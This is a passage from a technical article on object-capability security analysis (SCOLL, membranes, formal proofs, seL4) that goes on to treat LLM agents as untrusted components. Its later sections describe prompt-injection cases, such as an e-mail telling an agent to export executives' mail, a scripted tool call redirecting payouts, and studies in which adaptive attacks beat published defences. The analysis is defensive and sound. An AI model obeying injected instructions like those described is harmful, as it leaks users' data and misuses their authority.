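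The restriction about exchanges is an example of detail an analyst can add. The facts in the table above cannot express that Carol returns a valuable reference only in exchange for a secret token, so the coarse model has to include her giving it to everybody.

Spiessens adds a more specific fact, may.returnFor(B, X, Y), which means that B may return Y to a caller who sent X in the same call. It describes a narrower action, so it lets fewer interactions succeed. Existing descriptions remain valid, because a subject that may return Y unconditionally may also return it whatever the caller sent.

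The model of the caretaker must be refined too, or the extra detail about Carol makes no difference. In the coarse model, once one token holder has obtained the valuable reference through the caretaker, the caretaker can return it to any caller. In the refined model, the caretaker records which reference Carol returned for each argument, and can return that reference only to callers that supply the same argument.

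The results depend on the model's level of detail and on what the modeller assumes about Alice. The early version of the caretaker model, run on an incomplete implementation, had two solutions, while the version in the 2005 report has five. Spiessens found two in a simplified version and three in a fuller one. In every version, Carol must not return herself unconditionally, but the other things the programmer must avoid vary.

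More detail and more unknowns also make the search longer, even though each fixpoint is quick to calculate. When Spiessens asked for restrictions on both Alice and Carol, SCOLLAR found three solutions and then reached its 30-second limit. In another of his examples, a service writes its output to a file that the client chooses, so a client might trick it into overwriting its own file. With refined behaviour and two subjects to restrict, the analysis produced 25 alternatives. Jaradin and colleagues expected typical patterns to have fewer than ten roles.

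### The membrane

The caretaker is safe only if Carol behaves well, and often nobody can guarantee that. The membrane pattern removes this dependence by wrapping every reference that crosses between the two sides in a new proxy, so neither side ever receives a direct reference to the other. Each new proxy wraps references in the same way. If Carol returned herself through a membrane, Bob would receive a proxy for Carol, which would give him no more access than he had before.

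In Spiessens's SCOLL version, the two sides are Alice and Bob, and he relies on neither. Alice starts with a reference to proxyBob, which forwards to Bob, and Bob starts with a reference to proxyAlice, which forwards to Alice:

```
Alice ----> proxyBob ------> Bob
  ^                           |
  |                           v
  +-------- proxyAlice <------+
```

When Alice tries to introduce herself to Bob by sending proxyBob a reference to herself, proxyBob creates a new proxy with Alice as its target and sends Bob that proxy instead of the reference. proxyBob treats return values the same way, so the trick that defeated the caretaker fails.

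A running membrane may create an unlimited number of proxies, one for every reference that crosses it. Aggregation reduces them to two subjects. proxyAlice stands for every proxy whose target is on Alice's side, and proxyBob for every proxy whose target is on Bob's. Each subject is therefore both parent and child of the other, which would make no sense for individual objects but is a sound description of the two groups. When Bob receives a new proxy for an object on Alice's side, the model records that he has access to proxyAlice, which he already had from the beginning, and the calculation soon reaches its fixpoint.

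SCOLLAR found a single solution, which places no restrictions on Alice or Bob. Whatever code they run, neither can obtain a direct reference to the other. If one controller can also make every proxy stop forwarding, Alice can withdraw everything Bob has received through the membrane, including references she did not know had crossed. These guarantees depend only on the proxies' code being correct. Spiessens warns that an implementation may have trouble limiting the number of proxies, a problem that does not appear in the two-subject model.

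The SCOLL program for the membrane contains only safety goals. Proxies that ignored every message would also have met them, so the result shows that the two sides stay apart but not that they can work together. A membrane also does not stop Alice and Bob from influencing each other, since they can still use each other's services as long as the proxies forward messages. Spiessens argues that one cannot reasonably ask for more. If two untrusted subjects may use each other, each can use its own authority on the other's behalf, even if they never exchange a reference.

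### What the models leave out

Each call in a model carries at most one reference in and one reference out. An analyst has to split a call with several arguments into several calls, which loses the connection between them. She cannot express, for example, that Carol releases something only to a caller who presents two tokens together. The approximation is still sound, but it gives Carol's callers more than the code would. Spiessens sketches how to extend the model to several arguments, though the calculation then takes longer.

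Revocation means that the caretaker is no longer willing to forward, which the model can't express because it has no "not". The modelled caretaker therefore keeps forwarding forever, and the analysis checks whether Bob can obtain a direct reference to Carol while it does. If he can't, switching off the caretaker will cut off his only route to her. For a component that changes its behaviour in more complicated ways, Spiessens and colleagues suggest using two subjects, one for the behaviour before the change and one for the behaviour after it. The second subject stays passive until the triggering event has occurred, but the first remains active even then because the model has no notion of time.

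A more serious gap is how SCOLL and SCOLLAR treat data. A model can represent data only as a passive subject, one that never acts and that others can pass around like a reference. Data also travels in ways that references cannot. Jaradin and colleagues describe a component that accepts information from two clients, Alice and Bob, and writes it to a file without returning anything to either. If Alice can influence whether the component accepts a message, and Bob can observe whether it accepts his, she can send him information one bit at a time. Their analysis does not detect this channel. The fixpoint is a sound bound on who can obtain which reference, and on effects that depend on references. An analyst who wants to keep a secret from leaking must also model the flow of data, which the basic version of SCOLL does little to support.

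She also has to translate the software into a model by hand. Spiessens demonstrates this with a caretaker of about ten lines. If the incoming message is "revoke", the code sets a switch to "off". Otherwise, it forwards the message to Carol if the switch is still on. In the model, he ignores both tests and assumes that either outcome can occur. He omits the line that sets the switch because it gives nobody new authority. This leaves four rules: the caretaker accepts what callers send, passes it to Carol, accepts what Carol returns, and returns it to callers.

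An analyst can safely ignore a test, because doing so can only add to what the subject may do. But if the analyst overlooks a line that passes on a reference, the fixpoint will be too small and nothing in the calculation will reveal the error. The same can happen with components that are easy to miss, such as a module that the program loads indirectly or a class available to all the code. Spiessens advises analysts to look for these explicitly, and to group each unknown component with the other unknown components it can directly influence and with everything it can create.

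The system rules need the same care. In 1984, Boebert argued that capability machines could not keep secret information from flowing down to people without clearance. In his scenario, a program with low clearance stores its capability to write to a public file in that same file. A program with high clearance, which may read the file, takes the capability and can then write secrets to the file. Spiessens modelled this scenario in SCOLL with rules that let anyone who can read a file take capabilities out of it, and anyone who can write to a file put capabilities in. SCOLLAR found that the secret could leak. But these rules allow more than the capability system designed by Dennis and Van Horn does, because that system also has capabilities for segments that hold only data. The possible leak came from the coarse rules, and Spiessens points out that it proves nothing about real capability machines.

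Tools that extract models from program code would remove some of this risk. Spiessens left them outside the scope of his thesis, although he thought them crucial if many programmers were to use the method. Spiessens and colleagues also hoped that suppliers would one day attach a SCOLL description to their code. Customers could then check the code against the description and run the description through SCOLLAR with a model of their own software. In 2007, the solver was still a prototype, with a web interface where users could enter a pattern and see the resulting graph of references.

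## What has been proved about trusted code beside arbitrary code?

SCOLL's bounds hold for a model that an analyst has written by hand, and the model leaves out time and most of what data can do. Other researchers have proved theorems about more detailed models, down to the instructions that a processor executes. Their theorems share one form:

```
for every program A:   K running beside A satisfies P
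```

K is code that the analyst relies on and has described exactly. A is any program that the language or machine can run and that starts with only the references the analyst has listed. P is a property such as "the balance never falls".

Testing K against 500 known attacks shows that P holds against those 500 programs, but an attacker can write another. The proof also covers the new program because it assumes nothing about A except its starting references. However, it covers only P and attacks that the model can represent. For example, if the model lets only one component run at a time, the theorem does not rule out attacks that need two to run at once.

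### What concurrency changes

Murray, in *Analysing Object-Capability Security*, checked theorems of this form automatically. He used CSP (Communicating Sequential Processes), a notation for processes that interact through shared events, and FDR, a program that checks CSP models. Each object becomes a process, and each event is a call or a return that carries at most one capability. Murray wrote out the behaviour of the relied-upon objects in full. An untrusted object is a process with a set of capabilities that may, at any moment, do either of two things:

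- send a message to any object in its set, with any capability from the set or none;
- wait for a message, then add the sender and any capability in the message to its set.

This describes a program in a capability operating system, where processes run concurrently. In a single-threaded language, only one object is active at a time, so Murray's untrusted object acts only after it receives a message and becomes idle as soon as it sends one.

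FDR compares the modelled system with a specification that allows every sequence of events compatible with P. If the system can produce any other sequence, FDR prints it as a counter-example. The model must have finitely many states, so Murray borrowed aggregation from Spiessens to cover newly created objects. He tested three patterns in both settings:

| Pattern | Property | Single-threaded language | Concurrent system |
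|---|---|---|---|
| Membrane | Alice never calls Bob or Carol directly | holds | holds |
| Revocable membrane | Nothing passes once revocation is complete | holds | fails |
| Sealer-unsealer | Neither Alice nor Bob obtains the sealed object | holds | fails |

The revocable membrane checks a switch before it forwards each message. In the concurrent system, the membrane can find the switch on, then forward the message after the revoker has turned the switch off and reported that it has finished. The membrane won't forward later messages, so the leak is limited to calls already under way. Murray's thesis, *Analysing the Security Properties of Object-Capability Patterns* (2010), gives a weaker specification of revocation for concurrent systems.

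The sealer-unsealer pattern fails more seriously. A sealer puts a valuable reference in a box, which an untrusted messenger can carry but not open, and only the matching unsealer can get the reference out. In the version Murray tested, the boxes and the unsealer share a storage slot. The unsealer empties the slot, calls whatever it has received as a box, and looks in the slot again, because a genuine box will have put its contents there. Suppose Bob holds a box containing a reference to some cash, and Alice holds only the unsealer. She can get the cash as follows:

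1. Alice calls the unsealer and presents herself as the box.
2. The unsealer empties the slot.
3. Bob calls his box, which puts the cash in the slot.
4. The unsealer calls Alice, who simply returns.
5. The unsealer finds the cash in the slot and gives it to her.

FDR at first reported a leak in the single-threaded language too. In that counter-example, Alice answered another object before answering the unsealer, so Bob could run in between. Languages such as Joe-E, a restricted form of Java, do not allow this, because a call must return to its own caller first. After Murray excluded that sequence, the property held.

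Facts in a SCOLL model never expire, so a SCOLL model of this pattern would report the leak in both settings. That answer is sound, but it does not distinguish a language in which the pattern works from an operating system in which it fails. Murray's method can distinguish them, but it only checks behaviours the analyst supplies, whereas SCOLLAR can also search for safe ones.

His early models also missed attacks in which an object receives a second call before finishing the first. The methods in the thesis can detect these attacks, and the thesis extends results from small systems to systems of any size. It also proves that FDR cannot test certain properties exactly, including some simple ones about whether one object can cause an effect in a nondeterministic system.

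### What makes a value safe to share

FDR explores every behaviour of a finite model. Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens, in *Reasoning about Object Capabilities with Logical Relations and Effect Parametricity*, instead proved a theorem about every program in a language, a simplified JavaScript with no limit on the number of objects. They define which values are safe to share with unknown code, given a property P:

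- Plain data, such as a number or a string, is safe.
- A record is safe if all its fields are safe.
- A reference to memory or to a device is safe if every use of it respects P.
- A function is safe if, whenever it receives safe arguments, its effects respect P and its result is safe.

A definition of this kind is called a logical relation. The clause about functions is circular because it defines "safe" in terms of "safe". Devriese and colleagues avoid the circularity by counting steps of computation, so whether a function is safe for 10 steps depends only on which values are safe for fewer than 10.

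The main theorem is that any program whose variables hold only safe values respects P and produces a safe result. The language has only a few constructs, such as conditionals, loops, function calls and assignments. For each one, the proof shows that if the parts respect P, so does the whole. Every program is built from these constructs, so the theorem covers every such program, including those nobody has written yet.

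Some properties cannot serve as P. Controlling unknown code's references cannot force it to return a particular value, and if two actions are acceptable separately, the code may do one after the other. P can still limit sequences of actions if it refers to stored data, such as a flag in memory that records whether a program has already printed its single permitted line.

A counter that other code can only increase shows how the method works:

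```
n = 0
increment = function() { n = n + 1 }
read      = function() { return n }
```

The main program gives `increment` and `read` to unknown code but keeps the memory cell `n` to itself. P is that `n` never decreases, and we assume that numbers never overflow. In the terms of Devriese and colleagues, P is a state machine whose states are the values of `n` and whose permitted moves go upwards. The proof has three steps:

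1. `increment` moves the counter from `n` to `n + 1`, which P permits, and returns nothing of value. It is therefore safe.
2. `read` changes nothing and returns a number, which is plain data. It is therefore safe too.
3. The unknown code starts with only these two functions, so by the theorem, nothing it does can decrease `n`.

We never had to consider what the unknown code might be, but small changes to K would break the proof. If `read` returned the cell instead of the number, the unknown code could write any value to it. A function `add(k)` that adds its argument to `n` would also be unsafe unless it rejected negative arguments, because the unknown code may pass any plain data, including -5.

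Concurrency would break it as well. One call to `increment` might read 5 and pause while two others raise the counter to 7. When the first call resumes, it writes 6. The theorem is about a language that runs one step at a time, so it doesn't cover this case.

The main program might also keep a function that resets the counter. Devriese and colleagues allow for this by defining two sets of state changes, those that some part of the system may make and those that a given piece of code may make. Resetting is only in the first set, so one can still prove that the unknown code never itself decreases the counter.

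These results depend on the absence of ambient authority. In one example, Devriese and colleagues give unknown code a function that prints only in upper case, and they prove that all the output is in upper case. If every program could name the printer directly, unknown code could bypass the function, and the proof would fail because P would have to accept everything the printer can do. Even then, a bound on network use could hold if using the network still required a capability.

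### The same theorem for machine code

An attacker may supply machine code rather than JavaScript. *Cerise* (Georges, Guéneau and colleagues, 2021) proves a similar theorem for a capability machine, a processor that lets programs reach memory only through capabilities. Each capability records a range of addresses and a permission, such as read-only. Software can derive weaker capabilities from the ones it holds, but not stronger ones.

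On such a machine, the counter's code and its capability for the memory cell can be stored together in a private region. Outside code receives an entry capability, which it can jump to but cannot read through. When it jumps, the processor gives the counter's code permission to read the private region, and that code can then load the capability for the cell. Before returning control, the counter's code must clear that capability from the processor's registers, because the outside code can use any capability left there.

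Georges and colleagues call their theorem a universal contract because it gives a specification for arbitrary code. They used Coq, a program that checks mathematical proofs, to verify the theorem and their examples. They model a simplified version of CHERI, a real processor design, so the result does not cover mistakes in an actual chip. They also count a crash as safe. If unknown code attempts a forbidden access, the machine stops and the counter keeps its value, but nobody can read it. A theorem of this kind therefore doesn't rule out an attacker shutting the system down.

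A change to the instruction set can invalidate such a proof, because A might use any new instruction. *Formalizing, Verifying and Applying ISA Security Guarantees as Universal Contracts* (2023) describes a partly automatic method that makes the proof easier to redo. Checking the contract took 172 lines for a small capability machine and 215 for a version of RISC-V with memory protection.

*Cerisier* (Rousseau, Carnier and colleagues, 2026) extended the contract to programs whose status changes while the system runs. Suppose a client asks an unknown program to arrange a long calculation. The unknown program starts an enclave, a component with private memory whose identity the processor can certify from a hash of its code. The enclave calculates the answer and attaches a certificate, and the unknown program carries both back to the client. If the analyst has proved that this enclave certifies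 only correct answers, and the processor works correctly, then any answer that passes the client's check is correct, whatever the unknown program did.

### Calling unknown code in the middle of a task

Trusted code often has to call unknown code before finishing its own work, and the unknown code may then call back. *Necessity Specifications for Robustness* (2022) introduced specifications that limit when an effect can occur, such as a rule that an account's balance can fall only if somebody presents its key. Its proof method didn't yet allow the trusted module to call outside code.

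*Reasoning about External Calls* (Drossopoulou, Mackay and colleagues, 2025) removed this restriction. In its example, anybody with a reference to a shop's account can pay money into it, but withdrawing money also requires a key. To sell an item, the shop notes its balance and calls the buyer's `pay` method with a reference to the account. If the balance has risen by the price, the shop sends the item. The buyer is unknown code, so `pay` could do anything with what it can reach.

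Drossopoulou and colleagues prove that the call cannot reduce the balance if two conditions hold. Before the sale, the buyer must have no way to reach the key, directly or through other outside objects. The shop's module must also never leak a key or allow a withdrawal without one. The guarantee lasts only until the call returns, because the code that called the shop may legitimately hold the key and use it later.

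The second condition concerns the whole module. Drossopoulou and colleagues compare three versions of a module that share the same `transfer` method, which checks the key before it moves any money. In one version, nobody can change a key once it has been set. Another lets a caller change it by presenting the old key. Both are safe. A reviewer who read only `transfer` would miss the flaw in the third, which lets anybody replace the key at any time. An attacker can install a new key and use it to empty the account.

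The proof protects the balance and nothing else, and the shop as printed seems open to another trick. Suppose the balance is 100 and each item costs 10:

1. The buyer orders an item, and the shop notes a balance of 100.
2. The buyer's `pay` method pays nothing, but orders a second item.
3. The shop notes 100 again and calls `pay`, which this time pays 10.
4. The balance is now 110, so the shop sends the second item.
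5. The original sale resumes, finds a balance of 110, and sends the first item too.

The buyer gets two items for the price of one, unless the method that sends the items prevents it. The example omits that method's code. The proven specification still holds because the balance never fell. To rule out this trick, the analyst would have to add to P the requirement that each item have its own payment.

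### When the graph is the system

In some operating systems, the references themselves can be inspected. seL4 is a small kernel, the part of an operating system that controls all access to the machine, and its programs need capabilities for everything they ask it to do. Boyton (2009), in *A Verified Shared Capability Model*, used a proof-checking program to verify a model of seL4 based on the take-grant rules. Here K is the kernel, and A is any sequence of requests that programs make to it.

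Two components are connected if one can grant capabilities to the other or if they share storage for capabilities. Boyton's main theorem is that no sequence of requests can create a chain of connections between two components unless a chain already joined them at the start. Earlier models left out shared storage, which can spread authority unexpectedly. If Alice grants a capability to Bob, and Bob shares his storage with Carol, then Carol has it too, even though Alice has no right to grant her anything.

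Boyton derives from this theorem that a separate group of components can never gain more authority over an outside component than it had at the start. He also proves that if information has no path between two groups at the start, requests cannot create one. The second result covers only flows that capabilities authorise, so a program could still leak a secret by making a visible decision that depends on it.

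The proof that seL4's more detailed specification matched this model was unfinished in 2009, but the attempt had already exposed a defect in the kernel. The kernel checked a program's right to grant a capability when the operation began. If the operation was interrupted, the kernel could resume it without checking again, even if the right had since been revoked. The seL4 developers fixed this defect. Murray's revocable membrane has the same gap between check and use.

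A theorem about the kernel is useful only if the analyst knows which capabilities the programs start with. In earlier systems, she had to work this out from the code that distributed them. *capDL* (Kuz, Klein and colleagues, 2010) proposed a language for describing the distribution explicitly. A start-up program reads the description and creates the objects and capabilities it lists. A tool can also extract a description from a running system. The analyst therefore examines the same graph that the kernel enforces, instead of a separate model that may not match it. Kuz and colleagues described this as work in progress.

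One of their examples has a network driver and two client programs. They communicate through an endpoint, which is an object that the kernel provides for sending signals. The description lists these capabilities, among others:

| Holder | Object | Rights |
|---|---|---|
| Driver | shared endpoint | read, write |
| Driver | network card interrupts | read |
| Client 1 | shared endpoint | read, write |
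| Client 2 | shared endpoint | read, write |

Under Boyton's rule for information flow, the clients in this table are not isolated from each other, because Client 1 can write to the endpoint and Client 2 can read from it. This is true even if the driver's code is perfect. Separate endpoints would remove this path. The driver would still communicate with both clients, so the analyst would have to rely on the driver's code not to pass information between them.

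## Should a language model be treated as able to do anything?

Theorems about arbitrary code hold for any program that starts with only the references the analyst has listed. To apply them to a language model, the analyst has to say which references the model starts with. Strictly speaking, it has none, because the harness holds the mail password, the open connections and the tools.

### The model and the harness as components

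The simplest mapping treats the model and the harness as two components. The model is untrusted, so it gets SCOLL's MAXIMAL behaviour, and its only reference is to the harness. The harness is relied upon and holds the references to everything else. A tool call is a message from the model to the harness. In the diagram, the arrows on the left show text flowing into the model, and the arrows on the right mean "holds a reference to".

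```
user's request --+
web page --------+-->  Model ----> Harness ----> mailbox
tool output -----+                    |
                                      +--------> payment service
```

So far the model resembles Bob with his reference to the caretaker, and the bound depends on what the harness will forward. But the model requests a resource by writing a string, such as a file path or an account number. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) points out that in many coding agents, naming a resource is enough to act on it. The harness runs with the user's privileges and looks up whatever name the model wrote, much as `cp` opens whatever file names it receives.

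The model can write any string, so it can name anything whose name it can guess or has read. A file name is therefore not a capability. A long random string is closer to being one, since the model can't guess it. But once the model has read the string, it can repeat it in any message, including one that a stranger asks it to write.

Strings can still select capabilities if the harness looks them up in a table that contains only what this model may use. Similarly, `cat` refers to its open connections by small numbers, and it can try any number, but one that isn't in its own table gives it no access. CapScope, a system built by Bouras and colleagues, keeps each agent's table outside the model's reach. Each entry pairs a kind of effect (reading, writing or running a command) with a scope, such as every path below `src/`. The model proposes a call, and the harness carries it out only if an entry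 covers it. Bouras and colleagues do not call this an object-capability system, because the model still names resources by string and the table authorises the request afterwards. The bound depends on the set of calls that the harness will carry out if the model asks.

The model also reads text from many sources as one sequence. Bouras and colleagues count five places where an outsider's text can enter a coding agent: the project's documentation, an automatically loaded instruction file, reusable prompt files, comments in the source code, and the output of commands. Anyone who can write in one of these places is like Bob in the screen example, whose instructions Alice read and carried out. A programmer could rewrite Alice to ignore Bob, but nobody can make the corresponding change to a model and then check that it worked, so the analyst has to assume that every writer may steer the model.

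The analyst should not merge the model and the people who write its input into one subject. The merged subject would hold both a stranger's internet connection and the user's private mail, so the bound would include a leak even if the harness let nothing out. The stranger has to remain a separate untrusted subject that can send text to the model and receives only what the harness releases.

*OCapN and Structural Authority in Agentic AI*, a personal blog post by serefayar, instead draws the boundary around the whole agent. It treats the agent as a vat, an isolated unit of computation whose objects include the planner, memory and tool adapters. This mapping suits questions about what one agent can delegate to another. But an analyst who treats the vat as a single untrusted subject can no longer rely on the harness's code to limit what the agent does. Suppose the mail tool holds a password for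 the whole mailbox, but its code only saves drafts. If the analyst treats the model and harness separately, the bound includes only saving drafts, whereas treating them as one untrusted vat expands it to everything the password permits.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into misusing its authority. The name comes from a 1988 paper by Norm Hardy, whose example is a compiler. The compiler has permission to write to a billing file, where it records its users. It also lets each user name a file for debugging output. A user who has no permission to change the billing file can name it as the debugging file, and the compiler will overwrite the bills.

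With capabilities, the user gives the compiler a reference to an output file instead of a file name. She cannot give it a reference to the billing file because she has none. This remedy also depends on the compiler's code writing the debugging output through the user's reference and the bill through its own. A programmer can check this because the code keeps the two references in separate variables, and nothing in the user's input changes which variable a given line uses.

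A model doesn't keep its references apart in any way that a programmer can check. Suppose the harness gives it two references, one for writing to the user's accountant and one for writing to her landlord. She asks it to send her tax summary to the accountant. While doing this, the model reads an e-mail in which the landlord says that the summary should go to him as well. The landlord doesn't have to supply a reference or guess an address, because the model already holds a reference for writing to him and has proper uses for it. Whether it sends him the summary depends on how it interprets text that he partly wrote.

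Inside an agent, capabilities remove only the confused deputy cases in which an attacker names something that the agent holds no reference to. *Don't Prompt Your Agents. Equip Them* (2026), which presents a framework called Skillware, goes too far in claiming that replacing ambient authority with capabilities "eliminates the confused deputy vulnerability". In the paper's own example, a stranger's e-mail tells the agent to export executives' mail to an outside address through its mail tool. If the agent's job includes sending mail to outside addresses, it already holds a reference to that tool, so capabilities don't remove this case. The e-mail also supplies an argument that marks the export as confirmed, but anybody can write that string.

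Some cases of confusion are easier to catch. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines a confused deputy by comparing two permissions. If R is the set of permitted pairs of subject and resource, the agent is a confused deputy when:

```
(user, target) ∉ R     and     (agent, target) ∈ R
```

For example, suppose an employee asks for everyone's salaries, and the agent has administrative access to the personnel database. The harness can prevent the disclosure by checking the employee's permissions instead of the agent's. The same check would not stop the landlord, because the user has permission to write to him.

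Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined whether common software for building agents checks such things by default. He read the public code of LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to a payment company. He wanted to know whether anything decides, after the model has produced a tool call and before the call runs, that these particular argument values are permitted. In the versions he read, nothing did so by default:

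| Software | Default restrictions | Left to the model |
|---|---|---|
| LangChain / LangGraph | Only listed tools; usually also the form of the arguments | Argument values |
| LlamaIndex | Only listed tools | Argument values |
| Stripe Agent Toolkit | Only listed actions, within the scope of the account key | Amount, currency, customer, redirect address and others |

The agent can call only the tools on its list, so a tool's name works like the file descriptor numbers that `cat` uses. The account number in the call works like a file name given to `cp`, because it can refer to any account the payment service will accept.

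Mellafe Zuvic confirmed this with a simulated merchant account. He scripted a tool call that redirected the merchant's payouts to an attacker's account, and LangChain's normal machinery carried it out. A companion test with LlamaIndex gave the same result. The tests show what the software does with a bad call, not how often a model makes one. Developers can add checks or human approval themselves, and he did not examine what Stripe's remote service may do. He is the sole author and proposes his own remedy for the gap, but he pinned the code versions so that others can repeat the audit.

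### The case for assuming the worst

An analyst can rely on a caretaker because she can read its ten or so lines of code. A model's behaviour comes from a huge number of learned parameters, and there is no proof that a general-purpose model will never produce a given output.

Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, go further and argue that training cannot supply such a guarantee. A model reads the user's request and a stranger's document in a single stream of tokens, or pieces of words. The markers that show who is speaking are also tokens, so an attacker can write them too. A database avoids this problem by receiving a command and its data through separate channels, so no wording can turn the data into a command. Bhattarai and Vu's theorem is that if a system decides what counts as an instruction only from the content of the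 stream, an attacker could write some text that the model will, with non-zero probability, treat as a trusted instruction. The theorem also covers a second model that screens the same stream.

Bhattarai and Vu give only a sketch of a proof, and "non-zero" is a weak condition. A model that picks each token at random from its whole vocabulary gives every possible text some probability, though that probability may be far too small to matter. They say that the theorem does not imply that every deployment will fail, and that training can reduce attacks. But the theorem does undermine training as a source of guarantees, and a sound analysis would need guarantees to rely on training.

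The harness can impose limits that the model cannot. If the harness accepts only "yes" or "no" and discards any other answer, the model contributes one bit, whatever else it writes. The analyst can count on this limit because the harness enforces it.

Measured attack success rates also call for caution because they depend heavily on how hard the attacker tries. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences against prompt injection and against jailbreaks, in which users try to get a model to break its rules. Most of the original papers had reported attack success near zero. Attacks adapted to each defence, using methods that included automated search and human attackers, succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

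Two of these defences only change the text the model reads. Spotlighting marks trusted text with special delimiters, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. On AgentDojo, a benchmark that tests agents against prompt injection, fixed attacks succeeded as rarely as 1% of the time. An automated search that adapted its attacks raised the success rate above 95% against both defences. In a contest with more than 500 participants, people found 265 successful attacks on spotlighting and 178 on prompt sandwiching.

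Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers ample computing power and, for some attacks, access to the model's internals. They wanted to know whether a defence could be broken, rather than how many resources it would take. A worst-case analysis has the same aim, though an operator may also care about the resources required. Another study also got past all eight of the prompt-injection defences it tested, according to *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026).

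Newer models still attempt unauthorised actions. Mellafe Zuvic reports a test of 27 models in which the injected text presented a forbidden action as a step in the user's task. On average, the 12 cheaper models attempted the action in 60.3% of trials and the 15 flagship models in 18.9%. Individual models ranged from zero for Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview to 100% for GPT-4o mini. Bouras and colleagues planted instructions in small programming projects and found that one model, Qwen3.5-Flash, proposed the planted action in 34 of 75 runs under CapScope. Both experiments measured what the model tried to do, whether or not the harness allowed it.

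The assumption also means that the analyst doesn't need to know why a model misbehaves. Mellafe Zuvic points out that a model with a hidden trigger planted in training can produce the same malicious call as a model that has read a malicious e-mail, and that a check outside the model treats the two calls alike. The same applies to calls a model makes by mistake. *OverAct* (2026) measured tool calls that went beyond what the user had asked for, with no attacker involved, and found that they increased roughly in proportion to the number of unnecessary tools the agent was allowed to use. A bound that assumes arbitrary behaviour covers all three cases, and it still holds when the operator replaces the model.

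### The case against

Most models do roughly what their users ask most of the time. An analysis that treats a flagship model like a program written by an attacker discards everything testers have learned about it, so its bound is looser. If a mail assistant's harness passes on every request the model makes, the analysis counts every misuse of the user's correspondence as possible, however rare it would be in practice.

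Part of this problem is avoidable. In *OverAct*, restricting an agent to the tools its task required greatly reduced excess calls without lowering its task completion rate. But somebody must know in advance what the task needs, and the paper concedes that this is rarely possible in practice. Such restrictions also don't help when the task itself requires a dangerous combination of tools.

An analyst might instead replace MAXIMAL with a more realistic description of the model. SCOLL allows this for any subject, but while she could base the caretaker's description on its code, she would have to base the model's on test results.

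### Can a measured rate serve as a behaviour rule?

Suppose testers find that a model passes private mail to a stranger in 1% of attempted attacks. In SCOLL, the analyst has to decide whether the model's behaviour includes this fact:

```
may.sendTo(model, stranger, mail)
```

A fact in a SCOLL model means that the language model may do something, and omitting it means that the language model never will. A sound SCOLL model must therefore include the fact even if the language model does it only 1% of the time. Because SCOLL can't express how often it happens, the fixpoint is the same as if the rate were 100%.

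The analyst could round 1% down to zero and accept a small risk. But an attacker can try more than once. If each try succeeds with probability p and the tries are independent, then the probability that at least one of n tries succeeds is:

```
1 - (1 - p)^n
```

| Chance per try | 10 tries | 100 tries | 500 tries |
|---|---|---|---|
| p = 0.01 | 9.6% | 63% | 99.3% |
| p = 0.001 | 1.0% | 9.5% | 39% |
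| p = 0.0001 | 0.1% | 1.0% | 4.9% |

An assistant that reads 50 e-mails a day gives strangers 500 tries in ten days. To keep the total risk over those tries below 1%, the chance p that any one try succeeds would have to be at most about 1 in 50,000. Showing this with 95% confidence would take roughly 150,000 test trials without a failure.

Those trials would also have to use the attacks that the model will later face. In Mellafe Zuvic's data, Gemma 3 12B never attempted the forbidden action in 70 trials with a crude injection, which is consistent with a true rate as high as about 4%. When the injected text presented the same action as part of the user's task, the observed rate of attempts rose to 57%.

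The formula is approximate because real tries are not independent. If a model always gives the same answer to the same text, resending a failed message gains nothing. An attacker who learns from each failure and rewrites the message can do better than the formula predicts. Agents also repeat attempts without further help from the attacker. Bouras and colleagues saw the model propose the planted action in 34 runs, and 27 of those contained repeated calls aimed at that action.

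Rates also vary between models and between tests. In September 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) reported that OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra acted out of scope in simulations more often than previous OpenAI models. In OpenAI's own alignment tests, however, Astra was less likely overall than the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol to violate security and safety restrictions. Both results may be right, since the tests differ, but an analyst could not tell from either which rate to expect in her own deployment. OpenAI cautioned in a September note to its *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) that a lack of observed failures does not establish reliability across settings.

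Measured rates remain useful outside the worst-case calculation. The analyst can compute the fixpoint twice, first with MAXIMAL behaviour for the model and then with the behaviour that tests suggest. Any effect missing from the first fixpoint cannot be reached, whatever the model does. An effect that appears only in the first is ruled out only if this model behaves as it did in the tests. For such effects, the analyst can consider the measured rate together with the number of tries and the size of the harm.

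### The AIOracle formalism

Cryptographic proofs can allow for small chances of failure. Cryptographers define security as a game that an attacker tries to win, and call a system secure if no attacker with realistic computing power does much better than some baseline. One recent formalism applies this method to AI systems, in the hope of giving the many proposals for restricting agents a common basis for comparison.

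It represents a model, a chatbot or an agent as an AIOracle, a set of algorithms with two phases. The learning phase produces a model from data, and the inference phase takes a prompt, its context and the model, and returns a result. A predicate φ (a test with a yes-or-no answer) decides whether the result is valid for that prompt and context, meaning correct, useful and harmless. An AIOracle is p-complete if, with no attacker present, its results are valid with probability at least p. In the security game, the attacker may have any of several powers, such as adding training data, inspecting the model or writing part of its context, and wins by causing an invalid result. The attacker's advantage is:

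```
Adv = Pr[attacker wins] - (1 - p)
```

If a model fails 5% of the time on its own, and an attacker can make it fail 30% of the time, the attacker's advantage is 0.30 - 0.05 = 0.25. The system is secure to level ε if no efficient attacker has an advantage greater than ε.

Worst-case authority analysis assumes nothing about the model. The AIOracle definitions describe a model that fails with limited probability, even under attack, but they provide no way to show that an actual model meets this condition. Finding p or ε by testing is difficult because a program cannot compute φ. No algorithm can decide in general whether an answer is useful or harmless. Even a small ε covers only one game, so the risk accumulates over repeated attempts.

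The formalism's main construction uses two AIOracles. A "creative" one writes code to do what the user asked, and a "boring" one accepts or rejects that code according to rules about harm. The combination is provably complete and secure for the whole of φ if each oracle is complete and secure for its own part. The creative one must write code with enough structure and documentation for the boring one to check. Otherwise, the boring one should reject the code, and the user gets nothing.

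How much the construction assumes about the creative model therefore depends on the checker. Under the formalism, the checker may have to be about as complex as the model it checks. If the checker is a language model, an attacker can try to mislead it too, and whether the result is harmless also depends on the checker's failure rate. If the checker is a conventional program that verifies a proof about the code, it can be a relied-upon component, and the creative model can then be as untrusted as any program in Bob's place.

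## What bound results for an ordinary e-mail assistant?

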